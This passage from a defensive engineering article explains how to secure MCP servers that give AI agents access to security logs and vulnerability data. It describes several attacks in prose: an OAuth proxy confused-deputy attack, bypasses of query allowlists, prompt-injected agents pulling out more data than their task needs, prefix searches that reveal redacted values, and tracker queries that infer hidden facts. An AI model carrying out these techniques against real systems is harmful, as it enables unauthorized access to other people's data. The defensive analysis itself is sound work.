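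Dissanayaka explains that OAuth doesn't help here because it captures the user's consent only once, when the user grants access, and the agent may then make hundreds of calls the user never pictured. OAuth can confirm that the grant is valid, but "it does not tell you the agent should have wanted it."

Step-up authorization asks the user to approve broader access, but an attacker who controls the agent can trigger that prompt by having it call a tool that requires a broader scope. The analyst then sees a familiar sign-in page that names the scope but probably doesn't explain why the agent requested it. Dissanayaka thinks the agent's developers should check that each such request matches what the user intended. That is sensible, but a check inside the host does nothing against a script that has replaced the host. The invented company would do better to have the analyst add machines in the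 ticket system, where the incident's history is on the same screen.

### Passing a client's token downstream

Mediating servers often have to call another service, such as a SIEM's API. The Model Context Protocol specification forbids a server from accepting a client's token for the SIEM and forwarding it, a practice the protocol's security guidance calls token passthrough. Servers must reject any token that wasn't issued for them.

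The most serious problem with this design is that the client would hold a token that works directly on the SIEM. An attacker's script could use that token to bypass the mediating server and its row conditions, rate limits and audit records, so the assumption that every route to the data passes through the server would be false. A thief who obtained a SIEM token elsewhere could also use it to gain access through the mediating server, and the SIEM's logs might attribute requests to the wrong party.

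The server must therefore obtain a separate token for the SIEM, but whose rights the token should represent is still undecided. If the server requests the token in its own name, queries run under a service account that may be able to read everything. The server alone then has to keep the retail analyst from reading finance data, which is another instance of Hardy's confused deputy problem.

OAuth's token exchange extension avoids this. The server presents the analyst's token to the authorization server and receives a new one that still identifies the analyst but works only on the SIEM. The SIEM can then apply the analyst's permissions as a second check. The extra work is usually worthwhile if the SIEM supports token exchange.

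### The confused deputy in a proxy

Hardy's compiler misused its authority over a file. An MCP server that acts as a proxy for another company's service can misuse a user's consent. Model Context Protocol's guidance describes an attack on a proxy that uses one fixed client ID with the other company's authorization server, however many MCP clients connect to the proxy. The attack goes like this:

1. The analyst connects through the proxy and approves access. The other company's authorization server stores a cookie in the analyst's browser, recording that the analyst has approved the proxy's client ID.
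2. The attacker registers a new client with the proxy and gives an address of their own as the place to send authorization codes.
3. The attacker sends the analyst a link that starts a sign-in for this new client.
4. The analyst clicks. The authorization server finds the cookie, recognizes the proxy's client ID and skips the consent page.
5. The proxy sends a code to the attacker's address, and the attacker exchanges it for a token that acts as the analyst.

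The authorization server can't distinguish the attacker's client from the analyst's, because both arrive under the proxy's ID. The proxy can, so it has to ask for consent itself. The guidance requires it to record which clients each user has approved, check that record before forwarding anyone, and send codes only to the exact address the client registered. It must also set the cookie that tracks the sign-in only after the user approves, because otherwise the attacker could construct a link that bypasses the consent page.

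This attack requires no language model, and it gives an outsider full control over requests in the analyst's name.

### Handles for tasks

The server also has to track which incident each call belongs to. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is now stateless, so the server can't keep this information in a protocol session. The protocol's maintainers recommend that a server instead create a handle, an identifier for stored state, and return it to the model, which includes it as an argument in later calls. They found this works better than hidden session state because the model can see the handle and pass it from one tool to another.

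Showing the handle to the model helps the model but also makes the handle easy to leak. The handle is in the model's context, in saved conversations and perhaps in logs, and a manipulated agent can send it anywhere the agent can write. If the server numbers its handles in order, an attacker can guess them. If the server treated possession of a handle as proof of identity, anyone with the handle for a finance incident could get that incident's data.

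The specification's security guidance therefore says that servers must not treat possession of a handle as authentication. It recommends random handles, and storing the state under both the user and the handle:

```text
analyst-214:9f3c71e0b2  →  incident 4471
```

The server takes the first part from the verified token and the second from the agent's argument. If an agent sends a finance analyst's handle with analyst-214's token, the server finds nothing under that combination.

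This doesn't stop the agent from switching between the analyst's own incidents. If the analyst has five open incidents, each on three different machines, an agent that has all five handles can read 450 rows. A company that wants to limit the agent to 90 rows has to tie the token to the incident as well, for example by issuing a new token whenever the analyst opens an incident.

### How Sentinel and Splunk assign identity

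Microsoft's Sentinel server uses the analyst's own identity, through Microsoft's sign-in service, Entra. Its tools for sorting incidents can access only data that the user's existing role covers. However, the required Security Reader role gives read access to every workspace (a separate collection of tables) in Sentinel's long-term store. If the invented company kept its findings there, a retail analyst who received the role just to use the agent could read all 60,000 rows. Delegation would then protect the data no better than a shared service account does, though it would record more clearly who asked.

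Microsoft also has roles that cover a single workspace, but they don't reduce the access of someone who also holds Security Reader. More recently, Microsoft introduced a way to restrict users to particular rows, including in queries on the long-term store. A company that relies on this should sign in as a restricted analyst, call each MCP tool and check that the other units' rows are missing from the results.

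Splunk gives each user a separate encrypted token. According to Splunk's *Connecting to the MCP Server and settings*, this token works only on the MCP server and not on Splunk's API, so someone who steals it can't use it to bypass the server. Creating a token requires the `mcp_tool_admin` capability, which also lets its holder change the server's settings. Most analysts shouldn't have that capability, so an administrator has to create their tokens and hand them over. All tokens depend on one pair of keys, so an administrator who invalidates the keys in an emergency disconnects everyone.

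Newer versions let users sign in through a browser with OAuth, which avoids storing a long-lived token in the client's settings. According to Splunk's *OAuth for MCP Server*, only cloud customers can use this, and they should restrict clients to the scopes `openid` and `offline_access`. `openid` identifies the user, and `offline_access` lets the client renew its access when the user is away. Neither scope restricts what the client may read, so the user's Splunk role has to do that.

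In April 2026 Splunk (2026) disclosed CVE-2026-20205, a flaw in its MCP server that it rated 7.2 out of 10. Versions before 1.0.3 exposed users' session and authorization tokens in clear text in `_internal`, an index that holds Splunk's own logs. Users could read the tokens if their role gave them access to that index, which by default only administrators have, or if they held `mcp_tool_admin`.

That is a small group, but Splunk's MCP server lets agents search indexes, so an agent running with an administrator's permissions could presumably have found the tokens with an ordinary search. An attacker who controlled that agent could then have acted as any user whose token was still valid, and the logs would have recorded the actions under that user's name. The administrator's permissions in effect included those users' permissions too. Splunk advised customers to upgrade and to restrict the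 internal indexes to administrators. A company that ran an older version should probably also replace its tokens, because the upgrade may not remove old log entries.

### Who should carry the burden

MCP's maintainers leave many security decisions to the developers who build with it. Authorization is optional, the specification doesn't cover how the authorization server works, and each server decides which rows a user may see. In April 2026, OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* criticized this division of responsibility. It described a critical vulnerability at the core of MCP and called it an architectural design decision rather than a traditional coding error.

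The dispute concerns stdio servers, which the host starts by running a command from its configuration. If a product lets outside input reach that configuration, an attacker can insert their own command. OX Security reported that it had run commands on six production platforms, and that the problem had led to at least ten entries rated critical or high in the public catalog of vulnerabilities. Anthropic replied that the behavior was by design and a secure default, and that developers were responsible for sanitizing the input.

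Smimite, in *The 'mother of all AI supply chains' advisory*, considered the finding well reported but narrower than its headline. That seems right, because running a command is how a stdio server starts, and the flaw arises only where a product lets an untrusted person choose the command. But when many separate products make the same mistake, the default may encourage it.

The protocol can reasonably define the checks that are the same everywhere and leave the rest to the implementer. Every client can verify which authorization server sent a code, and the July revision made that check mandatory wherever the information is present. A rule that hosts must not start arbitrary programs could be nearly as universal. But no protocol can specify that a particular analyst may see retail data and not finance data, so the implementer will always have to handle those permissions.

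OX proposed four changes. Hosts would start servers only from a declared manifest, not from arbitrary command strings, and would block high-risk programs by default. Developers would have to explicitly switch on a "dangerous mode" before using changeable arguments, and marketplaces would require manifests signed by verified developers. Anthropic declined all four, according to flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report*, a blog post that sides with OX.

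These changes would help against a manipulated agent that can edit the host's configuration. Without them, the agent might start a program that reads a stored database password and bypasses the mediating server. They would not stop an agent with a valid token from calling `list_findings` and requesting more data than its task needs.

Researchers have also proposed a more thorough extension, the Secure Model Context Protocol (SMCP). It would verify the identities of agents and tools, have both sides of a connection authenticate each other, and attach security information to each call so that servers can apply detailed policies. The invented company could use this to establish *A* and *T* more reliably, since the server would have better evidence of which agent was calling and for what purpose. Someone would still have to write the policy that limits the incident to 90 rows. An agent manipulated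 by prompt injection would also still pass authentication, because the injection changes what the agent asks for without changing its credentials.

Under attested server admission, the host would connect only to servers that present a signed statement from a party it trusts, for example about who built the server and which version of the code it runs. This would keep the agent away from impostor servers, which can put hostile instructions in their tool descriptions. It would not stop hostile text in the data, because an attested server that returns a failed sign-in record also returns whatever the attacker typed as the username. Signed code can also have flaws. The versions of Splunk's own MCP server that exposed users' tokens were genuine Splunk software and could have passed such a check.

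## Choosing which queries the agent may send

The user, the agent and the task together determine which rows the agent may read, but the server has to apply those limits to every query. How hard that is depends on who writes the query. In the examples so far, the server wrote the SQL and the agent filled in a few values, but many real servers let the agent write the whole query.

### Four designs

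The most permissive design lets the agent write free-form queries in the data store's query language. A server can restrict these queries by checking each one against an allowlist of accepted commands before running it. A stricter server offers only fixed queries, which an administrator writes in advance, and the agent supplies only arguments, such as a severity level. The narrowest design gives the agent a function that does one job in ordinary code. The function may run several queries internally and return only a conclusion.

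| Design | What an investigator gains | What a manipulated agent could request |
|---|---|---|
| Free-form query | Answers to questions nobody foresaw, across several tables | Anything the database account may read or do |
| Free-form query with an allowlist | Nearly the same, without the commands left off the list | Anything the account may read through the allowed commands |
| Fixed query | Quick, repeatable answers to expected questions | The results of that query for any valid arguments |
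| Narrow function | One conclusion, possibly drawn from several systems | That conclusion for any valid input |

A command allowlist limits what a query can do, but usually not which data the query can read. An agent allowed to use only a `search` command can still search every log the analyst has permission to see.

A function can reveal much less. For example, it could take a machine's name and report only whether that machine has a critical flaw more than 30 days old. A manipulated agent that called it for every retail machine would get 400 yes-or-no answers instead of 12,000 rows. Salesforce's *Security Best Practices* recommends custom tools of this kind for access rules that ordinary permissions can't express. But somebody has to write and maintain each function, and a bug in one with broad database access could expose more than the intended answer.

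### Free-form and saved queries in Sentinel

Microsoft's Sentinel server offers both free-form and fixed queries. Its `query_lake` tool takes any single query in KQL, Microsoft's query language for logs, and returns the raw results. Another tool, `search_tables`, finds tables that match a plain-language description. Microsoft shows an agent using both to find the three users most at risk. The agent found four relevant tables, searched again with broader terms, and wrote a query that failed. It then corrected the query, got the names, and ran another to find out why those users were at risk.

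A manipulated agent could use the same tools to find the most sensitive tables and read them. Microsoft describes `query_lake` as a tool for focused retrieval, not bulk export, but a description only guides the model. Microsoft also lists an 800-character query window for Sentinel's data lake tools. This limit does little to prevent theft, because in KQL a table's name alone is a valid query for its contents.

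Security teams can also turn a saved KQL query into a separate tool. Amdursky (2025), in *Microsoft Sentinel MCP server*, notes that many organizations already keep libraries of such queries for triage and threat hunting. The team replaces some values in the query with named parameters and describes them so that the model can fill them in. The invented company could fix the table, the columns and most of the conditions, and let the agent choose only the severity. Sentinel keeps the tool in sync with the saved query, so anyone who edits the query changes what agents can obtain. The company should review those edits as carefully as changes to the server's code.

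Custom tools give the granular control over agents' data access that Microsoft describes only if the agent can't also call `query_lake`. The Security Reader role is enough to call either, so a script with the analyst's credential could ignore the custom tools and send its own KQL. A custom tool's default workspace doesn't confine the agent either, because it is only a hint for prompts that don't name a workspace. To enforce the limits, the company could put its own server in front of Sentinel, keep the Sentinel credential there and expose only the custom tools.

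### Allowlists, templates and roles in Splunk

A search in Splunk's language, SPL, is a chain of commands, each passing its results to the next. When an agent uses Splunk's main search tool, `splunk_run_query`, the server checks these commands against an allowlist of safe ones before it runs the search. According to Splunk's *MCP Server tools*, a search can also fail if it takes more than a minute or returns more than 1,000 events.

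The list of permitted commands used to be the same for every customer. Version 1.3.0, which Splunk's *MCP Server release notes* date to 22 July 2026, let administrators add their own commands. Radidiya's *Splunk MCP Server 2.0* explains that administrators can later disable or remove these additions but can't change the built-in defaults. Any user can look up the list to see why the server rejected a query. All clients share one list, so a command that an administrator adds for one team's task becomes available to every agent with access to the search tool.

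A command can be harmless to the system and still reveal a lot. The default list now includes `rest`, which lets an agent look up which apps the company has installed and how it has configured them. This information is useful to administrators, but it would also help an intruder learn how the company detects attacks. The search tool also now accepts SPL2, a newer version of Splunk's search language, and one SPL2 query can cover connected data sources outside the local Splunk system. The tool may therefore reach more data today than an administrator approved a year ago.

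Splunk also supports fixed queries. Splunk's *Create MCP tools using the Create Tool feature* explains that an administrator can write an SPL template and give each argument a name, a description and a type. The administrator can also decide whether the agent may choose the time range. Creating a tool requires the `mcp_tool_admin` capability, and custom tools are unavailable until somebody enables them.

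Administrators can then map roles to individual tools. Radidiya reports that the server enforces this mapping both when it lists tools and when a user calls one, so users can neither see nor call a tool that their role isn't mapped to. Only the check on calls stops an attacker's script, while hiding the tool keeps an ordinary agent from making calls that would fail. The invented company could give retail analysts a few templates and reserve `splunk_run_query` for senior investigators. The mapping is optional in Splunk, so an administrator has to set it up.

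### Why checking the text of a query is hard

An allowlist works only if the server correctly determines what a query will do. The server parses the text to check it, and the data store parses it again to run it. Let *C*(*q*) be the set of operations that the checker finds in a query *q*, and let *D*(*q*) be the set that the data store performs. The list is a real limit only if

```text
D(q) ⊆ C(q)   for every query q
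```

An attacker needs only one query for which this is false. The difference may not be visible in the query's text, because a query can call a stored function or macro whose commands are defined elsewhere.

SPL allows a search to contain another search, called a subsearch, whose results feed into the outer one. In December 2025, Splunk (2025) disclosed CVE-2025-20381, a flaw that let users bypass the allowlist by putting commands in a subsearch. A Splunk employee found the flaw, and version 0.2.4 fixed it. Splunk rated its severity 5.4 out of 10, with a limited effect on integrity and availability and none on confidentiality. That rating is plausible if searches ran with the user's own permissions, because those permissions would still have kept users away from other people's data.

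Anthropic's reference server for the PostgreSQL database had a more serious flaw. To let agents read data without changing it, the server opened a read-only transaction (a group of operations in which the database refuses changes) for each call, ran the agent's text inside it and then rolled it back. Datadog's *MCP vulnerability case study* (2025) explains that the server handled the text as one query, but the database library accepted several statements at once. One statement could end the read-only transaction, and later ones could then change or delete data.

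The fix took only a few lines of code. The server sends the query text as a prepared statement, which PostgreSQL limits to a single statement, and closes the connection after each call. Otherwise, a query could change a connection setting, such as the time limit, and make the next user's queries fail, even if the database account had few privileges.

A researcher first reported the flaw in November 2024, eight days after the server's release. Anthropic fixed the source code in May 2025 and archived the server the same day, but did not publish a fixed package. In August, Datadog found that people were still downloading the vulnerable package about 21,000 times a week.

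Developers of other servers made similar mistakes:

- OSV's *CVE-2026-48774* (2026) describes a "read-only" tool in the database proxy ProxySQL. It searched the text for forbidden words and checked the first keyword, but MySQL could still run additional statements that changed data.
- Postgres MCP Pro checked function names in most of a query but skipped those in the FROM clause, which names the query's sources. VulnCheck's *Postgres MCP Pro 0.3.0 Restricted-Mode Bypass via FROM-Clause Function* says attackers could use this to read files on the server, and rates the flaw 9.2 out of 10.
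- Researchers at Akamai, an internet infrastructure company, reviewed about 300 official MCP servers and reported flaws in three. The server for the Apache Pinot database checked only that a query began with SELECT. The one for Apache Doris checked the start of the query but pasted an unchecked database name in front of it.

A server that has to accept free-form queries can reduce the risk by parsing each one with the data store's own parser, accepting only one statement and rejecting any construct that its checker doesn't recognize. It can then build a new query from the parsed form and send that instead of the agent's original text. This is a lot of work for a rich query language, and each upgrade of the data store may add syntax that the checker has to cover.

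The database can also enforce limits itself. AWS's *CVE-2026-85787* (2026) reports that Amazon's PostgreSQL server used an incomplete list of forbidden inputs, so crafted SQL could modify data. AWS fixed the list but calls a database account with minimal privileges the strongest control, because its limits apply to any SQL that reaches the database. AWS also warns against connecting with administrator accounts, which bypass row-level security.

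VMware's *Your Database Is About to Become an AI Tool. Is It Ready?* argues instead that the MCP server, not the database's own access controls, is the security boundary. Its author built a prototype that parses every query and rejects any with more than one statement. For free-form queries AWS has the better argument, because a restricted account limits *D*(*q*) even when the checker misses something. In practice the two positions are closer, because the VMware article also insists on a read-only database connection and says that every other control depends on it.

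### One task as a free-form query and as a fixed query

Suppose the analyst wants to find retail machines that face the internet and have had a critical flaw open for at least 30 days. The retail unit has 40 internet-facing machines, none of which are payment servers, and a second table called `assets` records which machines they are. With a free-form tool, the agent might write:

```sql
SELECT f.host, count(*) AS open_flaws, max(f.days_open) AS oldest
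FROM findings AS f JOIN assets AS a ON a.host = f.host
WHERE f.business_unit = 'retail'
  AND a.internet_facing
  AND f.severity = 'critical' AND f.days_open >= 30
GROUP BY f.host ORDER BY oldest DESC;
```

This works, and the agent could also group the results by software package or compare them with sign-in records. But the retail condition is now part of the query text the agent writes, so a manipulated agent could omit the whole WHERE clause and request every column. The agent would still get only 11,400 rows if the database itself applied the analyst's rights and the company's rule about payment servers, but it would get all 60,000 if the server relied on the query text to restrict access.

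As a fixed query, the same task looks like this:

```sql
SELECT f.host, count(*) AS open_flaws, max(f.days_open) AS oldest
FROM findings AS f JOIN assets AS a ON a.host = f.host
WHERE f.business_unit = $1          -- from the verified identity
  AND f.host_group <> 'payments'    -- company rule for agents
  AND a.internet_facing             -- written in advance
  AND f.severity = $2               -- from the agent
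  AND f.days_open >= $3             -- from the agent
GROUP BY f.host
ORDER BY oldest DESC, f.host
LIMIT $4;                           -- from the agent
```

The answer depends only on the 1,200 findings for those 40 machines, whatever arguments the agent sends. The query therefore sets the limit *T* by itself, and nobody has to list the machines in a ticket first. A manipulated agent could work out how old each finding is by repeating the call with different ages, but it could not learn which packages have the flaws, because the query never returns that information.

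The server describes the tool to agents with this definition:

```json
{
  "name": "list_exposed_machines",
  "description": "Lists your internet-facing machines with open flaws.",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "severity": {
        "type": "string",
        "enum": ["low", "medium", "high", "critical"]
      },
      "min_days_open": {
        "type": "integer", "minimum": 0, "maximum": 3650
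      },
      "limit": {
        "type": "integer", "minimum": 1, "maximum": 50
      }
    },
    "required": ["severity", "min_days_open", "limit"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

If the server validates calls against this schema, it rejects arguments such as these:

| What the agent sends | Why the server rejects it |
|---|---|
| `"severity": "critical or high"` | The value is not one of the four allowed |
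| `"min_days_open": "30"` | The value is text, not an integer |
| `"min_days_open": -1` | The value is below the minimum |
| `"limit": 5000` | The value is above the maximum |
| `"business_unit": "finance"` | The tool has no such argument |
| No `severity` at all | The argument is required |

Developers easily forget the last line of the schema, which sets `additionalProperties` to false. Without it, JSON Schema allows arguments that aren't defined, so a call that included `business_unit` would pass validation. This is harmless as long as the code ignores the extra argument, but a later developer might forward every argument to the query.

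After validation, the server passes the values to the database in a parameterized query. Query parameters can hold values but not the names of tables or columns. Google's Model Context Protocol Toolbox, a server that connects agents to databases, handles names with "template parameters", which it inserts into the SQL as text. According to its documentation, these are prone to SQL injection and should be restricted to a list of allowed values. To let the analyst choose how to sort the machines, the tool could accept "age" or "count" and have the server translate that into a column name.

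None of these checks can detect a bad motive. A request for every internet-facing machine with a critical flaw is valid whether it comes from an analyst who wants to patch the machines or an intruder who wants to attack them.

### Why the business unit must come from the verified identity

If the schema included a `business_unit` argument with the company's units as the allowed values, "Finance" would pass every check, because the schema defines which values are valid, not who may use them. A rule in the system prompt wouldn't stop a manipulated agent from sending that value. The server could compare the argument with the unit in the company's directory, but then it would already have the right value and wouldn't need the agent's.

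An analyst who covers two units may want to see results from only one. The tool can accept a unit as a filter, provided that the server also limits results to the units tied to the analyst's verified identity, so that the agent's choice can narrow the results but never widen them.

Google Cloud's *Use parameterized views in agentic applications* gives the same rule for its Bigtable database. Values such as the user's identity must come from trusted application code, never from the model or the end user. In Google's example, the application signs the user in and stores the identity where the model can't see or change it. The model chooses only ordinary filters, such as a city. The tool then adds the identity and runs the query on a view, a stored query that behaves like a table. The application's account can read the view but not the table behind it. Oracle's *Database Session Identity and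 Role Propagation* describes a similar design, in which Oracle's server passes the user's identity into the database session and the database uses it to filter rows.

The trusted code in Google's example is part of the application that runs the agent. This protects the user's identity from a misled model, but if the application ran on the analyst's computer, an attacker who took over that computer could replace the application and supply any identity. The invented company's server therefore takes the user's identity and unit only from the token it has validated, and ignores anything else about them in the client's message.

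### Whether fixed queries cripple an investigation

Fixed queries can answer only questions that somebody has foreseen, and investigations often raise others. Datadog acknowledges this in its account of the PostgreSQL flaw. It says a traditional application would never run arbitrary SQL from a user, but agents often need more open-ended tools, and their business needs often conflict with traditional security measures.

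Suppose the analyst learns at two in the morning that the intruder's malware leaves behind a file with a particular name. If none of the company's 30 fixed queries searches by file name, the agent can't continue until an administrator writes one that does. The analyst might instead export the whole log and give it to the agent as a file, bypassing the mediating server. An overly strict set of tools can therefore leave the company worse off than a broader one.

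Still, much of the work is routine, and fixed queries often do it better. Microsoft recommends them for incident response because the same query runs every time. In its example, one engineer finds a problem in five minutes, while another makes little progress in 30 minutes of improvised queries. The example is a vendor's illustration, not a measurement, but agents that write their own queries also make mistakes, as the failed first attempt in Sentinel showed. An agent can also combine fixed queries, for example by listing the exposed machines and then looking up recent sign-ins on each, so 30 queries can answer far more than 30 questions.

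For the remaining questions, the company can grant a broader tool case by case. Salesforce advises its customers to start with the most restrictive configuration that meets their needs and to expand access only when necessary. The invented company could keep its free-form tool off by default and let a senior investigator turn it on for one analyst and one incident, with an expiry time. The server would check the grant on every call. An administrator could do something similar with Splunk's role mapping by giving the analyst a role that includes `splunk_run_query` and removing the role afterward. Like the list of machines in an incident, the grant has to come from somewhere the agent can't write to, such as the ticket system.

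The tool also has to be unavailable the rest of the time. The VMware article argues that agents with purpose-built tools have less reason to write complex queries. That is probably true in ordinary use, but it doesn't stop an attacker's script from sending them.

A free-form grant does not have to weaken the guarantee for the other business units. If the tool uses a database account that can read only the retail rows, the other 48,000 rows stay out of reach whatever SQL the agent writes, unless the database itself has a flaw. The grant does expose more of the retail data. In the example above, the agent could read 11,400 rows instead of getting summaries of 1,200, and it could combine them in ways nobody has reviewed.

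Analysts also tend to need a grant for the broader tool during a suspected break-in, when the logs are most likely to contain text planted by an intruder. The grant should therefore cover only the tables the analyst needs and last for hours, not weeks. If analysts need a grant every day, the set of fixed queries is too small, and administrators should turn recurring free-form queries into new tools.

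How freely a company can grant access to a free-form query tool depends mainly on its data store. If the database reliably filters rows by the analyst's identity, the tool puts little at risk beyond what the analyst may already see, and refusing it may do more harm than good. If the only limit is a program that inspects the query's text, the flaws of 2025 and 2026 are a good reason to keep the tool off.

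## Limiting what each answer, and all answers together, reveal

If a developer forgets the business-unit condition in a new tool, the agent can read all 60,000 rows unless the database enforces the limit too.

### Enforcing the permitted view in the database

Databases can apply the limit in several ways. A restricted view can show the server's account only some rows, such as the retail rows. Column permissions let an account read only some columns, so the company could withhold a column of administrators' notes. Query rewriting adds conditions to each query before it runs. With row-level security, the database does this itself, using a policy that an administrator attaches to the table. Row-level security probably suits the invented company best, because one policy covers all its units, whereas the company would need a separate view for each.

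In PostgreSQL, the policy could look like this, where `mcp_reader` is the server's database account:

```sql
ALTER TABLE findings ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;
ALTER TABLE findings FORCE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;

CREATE POLICY unit_only ON findings
  FOR SELECT TO mcp_reader
  USING (business_unit = current_setting('app.unit', true)
         AND host_group <> 'payments');
```

The policy compares a column with a session setting, a common pattern that OreStudio's *PostgreSQL Row-Level Security* also describes. Suppose a new tool lacks the unit condition. The server validates the analyst's token, finds the retail unit in the company's directory and sends this:

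```sql
BEGIN;
SELECT set_config('app.unit', 'retail', true);
SELECT host, package, days_open FROM findings
WHERE severity = 'critical' AND days_open > 30;
COMMIT;
```

PostgreSQL in effect changes the last query's condition to:

```sql
WHERE (business_unit = 'retail' AND host_group <> 'payments')
  AND (severity = 'critical' AND days_open > 30)
```

The agent therefore gets results from the 11,400 retail rows that agents may read. The `true` in `set_config` makes the setting expire with the transaction, so the next analyst whose query uses the same connection doesn't inherit it. If the server doesn't set the unit, no row matches and the agent gets an empty answer. The data stays safe, but the analyst could wrongly conclude that no machine has the flaw, so the server should treat a missing unit as an error.

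According to PostgreSQL's manual, superusers and accounts with the `BYPASSRLS` attribute always bypass row policies, and a table's owner normally does too, unless an administrator sets `FORCE`. Views can also bypass the caller's row policies, because a view normally applies its owner's policies unless the developer turns on `security_invoker`. Tessl's guide to row security says this option was introduced in PostgreSQL 15.

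This policy works with fixed queries but not with free-form ones. `set_config` is an ordinary function, so a manipulated agent that writes its own SQL could call it and change the unit to finance. For free-form queries, the server should log in with a separate database account for each unit, and the policy should depend on the account instead of a setting.

The second check also can't catch a mistake about who is asking, because the database gets the user's identity from the server. If the server uses one shared account and passes no identity along, the database can't tell users apart. *Data Agents Under Attack* (Wang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested four open-source systems that let agents analyze databases and two commercial ones, Databricks and BigQuery. One attack, which planted false claims about access rights in the data, succeeded 24 to 56% of the time on the open-source systems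 and never on the commercial ones, which ran under restricted roles. The roles may not fully explain the difference, since the Databricks agent often refused attacks by citing its policy.

Sentinel's row-level scoping, which Microsoft announced as a public preview in March 2026, tags rows as they arrive. According to Microsoft's instructions, it can't tag rows already in storage, and analysts with a scope don't see untagged rows. If the company turned scoping on last month, a retail analyst couldn't see earlier rows. Scopes are also additive, so a broader role in Entra overrides them. The Security Reader role that analysts need for the MCP tools is an Entra role, so it may override their scope.

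### Redacting credentials and personal data

Rows inside the permitted view can still contain things the agent doesn't need, such as passwords. Errico, Ngiam and Sojan (2025), in *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, recommend output checks and data-loss-prevention software, which looks for sensitive data on its way out. A mediating server can replace whatever looks like a credential or personal data before it returns an answer. Suppose a search returns these three log entries:

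```text
GET /reports?token=eyJhbGciOiJIUzI1NiJ9...  from 203.0.113.7
failed sign-in: user "Harbor-Violet-82"     from 203.0.113.7
failed sign-in: user "m.okafor"             from 203.0.113.7
```

The server can recognize the access token by its form and remove it. It will probably miss `Harbor-Violet-82`, a password someone typed into the username box, because that string could also be an unusual username. The server could catch the password by removing all usernames and addresses as personal data, but then the analyst couldn't see that one address had tried several accounts, which may be the best evidence of an attack.

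*ToolMinimize* (2026), which covers data that agents send to outside tools, finds similar faults in redaction software. The software misses text that is sensitive only by implication, such as the name of a cancer hospital, and redacts the same way no matter how trustworthy the recipient is. In security data, a machine name like `payroll-db-01` contains no secret, but an intruder can use it to work out where to look.

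For usernames and addresses, the server can replace each value with a code that stays the same wherever the value appears, such as `addr-4c1e`. The agent can then see that three entries share an address, and the analyst can look up the real one in the SIEM. The server has to compute the code with a secret key, because an attacker could reverse an ordinary hash by hashing all 4.3 billion IPv4 addresses and looking for a match. The agent can't compare a coded address with a list of known attackers' addresses, so the server needs a separate function for that.

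The server has to redact data before it applies the agent's filters. If it hides usernames in its answers but lets the agent search for those that start with "H", then "Ha", then "Har", the agent can work out the hidden value one character at a time by seeing which searches return a match. A 16-character value takes at most 1,520 searches, since there are 95 printable characters to try in each position.

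### Limits on rows, calls and time

Suppose the server returns at most 1,000 rows per call and accepts 10 calls a minute. A script needs 12 calls to copy the retail unit's 12,000 rows. If the server counts calls in fixed one-minute windows, the script can copy all the rows within seconds by making 10 calls at 9:00:58 and the last two at 9:01:00, when the counter resets.

A sliding window, which counts the calls in the past 60 seconds, would only delay the last two calls by about a minute. To make the copy take 30 days, the company would have to set a limit of 400 rows a day, and an analyst looking into incidents of 90 rows each would reach it during the fifth. Without that daily limit, a patient attacker could take 100 rows an hour and finish in five days. Row and rate limits therefore slow copying and make hurried copying easy to notice, but they don't prevent it. Errico and colleagues warn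 that an attack that resembles normal use may not show up in logs.

The documented limits for Splunk's MCP server and Sentinel's data lake tools differ a lot:

| | Splunk MCP server | Sentinel data lake tools |
|---|---|---|
| Size of one answer | 1,000 events | 500,000 rows or 64 MB |
| Time for one query | 1 minute | 4 minutes, with a 120-second limit on MCP streaming |
| Calls per minute | No limit until an administrator sets one | 30 |
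| Queries at once | Not specified | 10 |
| Who shares the call limit | All callers on one node | The whole organization |

Splunk made rate limiting generally available in May 2026. Splunk's *MCP Server rate limiting* describes fixed one-minute windows like those in the example, with limits for the whole server and for individual tools. Each node (one of the machines running Splunk) keeps its own count, so a limit of 10 on a three-node system could allow 30 calls. Splunk also has a default row limit, but it applies only when the caller doesn't specify one.

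In Sentinel, the company's entire findings table would fit in one answer if its rows averaged less than about 1 KB. Microsoft sets no limit per user, so a single manipulated agent could use up all 30 queries allowed each minute and lock other analysts out during an attack. In April 2026, Sentinel gained thresholds that block new queries once an organization exceeds its usage limit. *Enforce Cost Limits on KQL Queries and Notebooks* (shubh_khandhadia, 2026) presents them as a way to control costs, but they might also stop a very large theft.

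Time limits mainly protect availability. In one of Wang and colleagues' tests, an agent tried to combine every row of one 13.8-million-row table with every row of another. The system had no way to cancel the query and stopped responding for 30 minutes.

### Working out hidden facts from permitted answers

So that retail analysts can compare their unit with others, the company also lets their agents count machines in any office, as long as each count covers at least 10 machines. An agent learns that 7 of the 41 machines in one finance office lack an openssl patch. It then asks about the same office without the server fin-0009 and learns that 6 of the other 40 machines lack the patch, so fin-0009 must be unpatched.

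The rule allows both counts. The server also keeps its guarantee, because the counts are part of the permitted view and the guarantee doesn't cover what someone can infer from them.

Refusing questions that exclude one machine wouldn't solve the problem. In *The Tracker* (1979), Denning, Denning and Schwartz showed how to get the answer to a forbidden question from permitted ones. Let *C* be the condition "is fin-0009 and lacks the patch". It matches one machine or none, so the server refuses to count it. The agent picks an unrelated condition *T*, such as "runs Linux", which matches 800 of the company's 2,000 machines, and asks for two counts:

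```text
count(C or T) + count(C or not T) = 2,000 + count(C)
```

The equation holds because every machine matches either *T* or "not *T*", so the sum counts each machine once and counts any machine that matches *C* a second time. If the answers are 800 and 1,201, they add up to 2,001, so fin-0009 is unpatched. Denning and colleagues called a condition like *T* a tracker. With a minimum group of 10, any condition that matches between 20 and 1,980 machines can serve as a tracker, even if the server also refuses counts over 1,990. The same tracker works for every machine in the company. Denning and Schlörer (1980) found that their procedure for finding a tracker often took just a few queries.

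Fixed queries make this harder, since an agent that can supply only an office and a patch can't write "*C* or *T*". But the company still has to check how its groups overlap. If another tool counts machines by team, and one team has every machine in the office except fin-0009, the agent can do the same subtraction.

### Auditing the whole series of queries

A server can also keep a history of each user's queries and refuse any query whose answer, combined with earlier answers, would reveal too much. Database researchers call this query auditing. Dobkin, Jones and Lipton (1979) studied a rule that limits how many records two queries may share. Suppose each query adds up a value over at least 10 machines, any two queries share at most one machine, and the attacker knows none of the values in advance. The attacker then needs at least 2 × 10 − 1 = 19 queries to work out any single value. Under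 such a rule, though, an analyst could hardly ask two questions about the same office. The bound also doesn't hold for yes-or-no facts, because a single count of 0 unpatched machines reveals that every machine in the group is patched.

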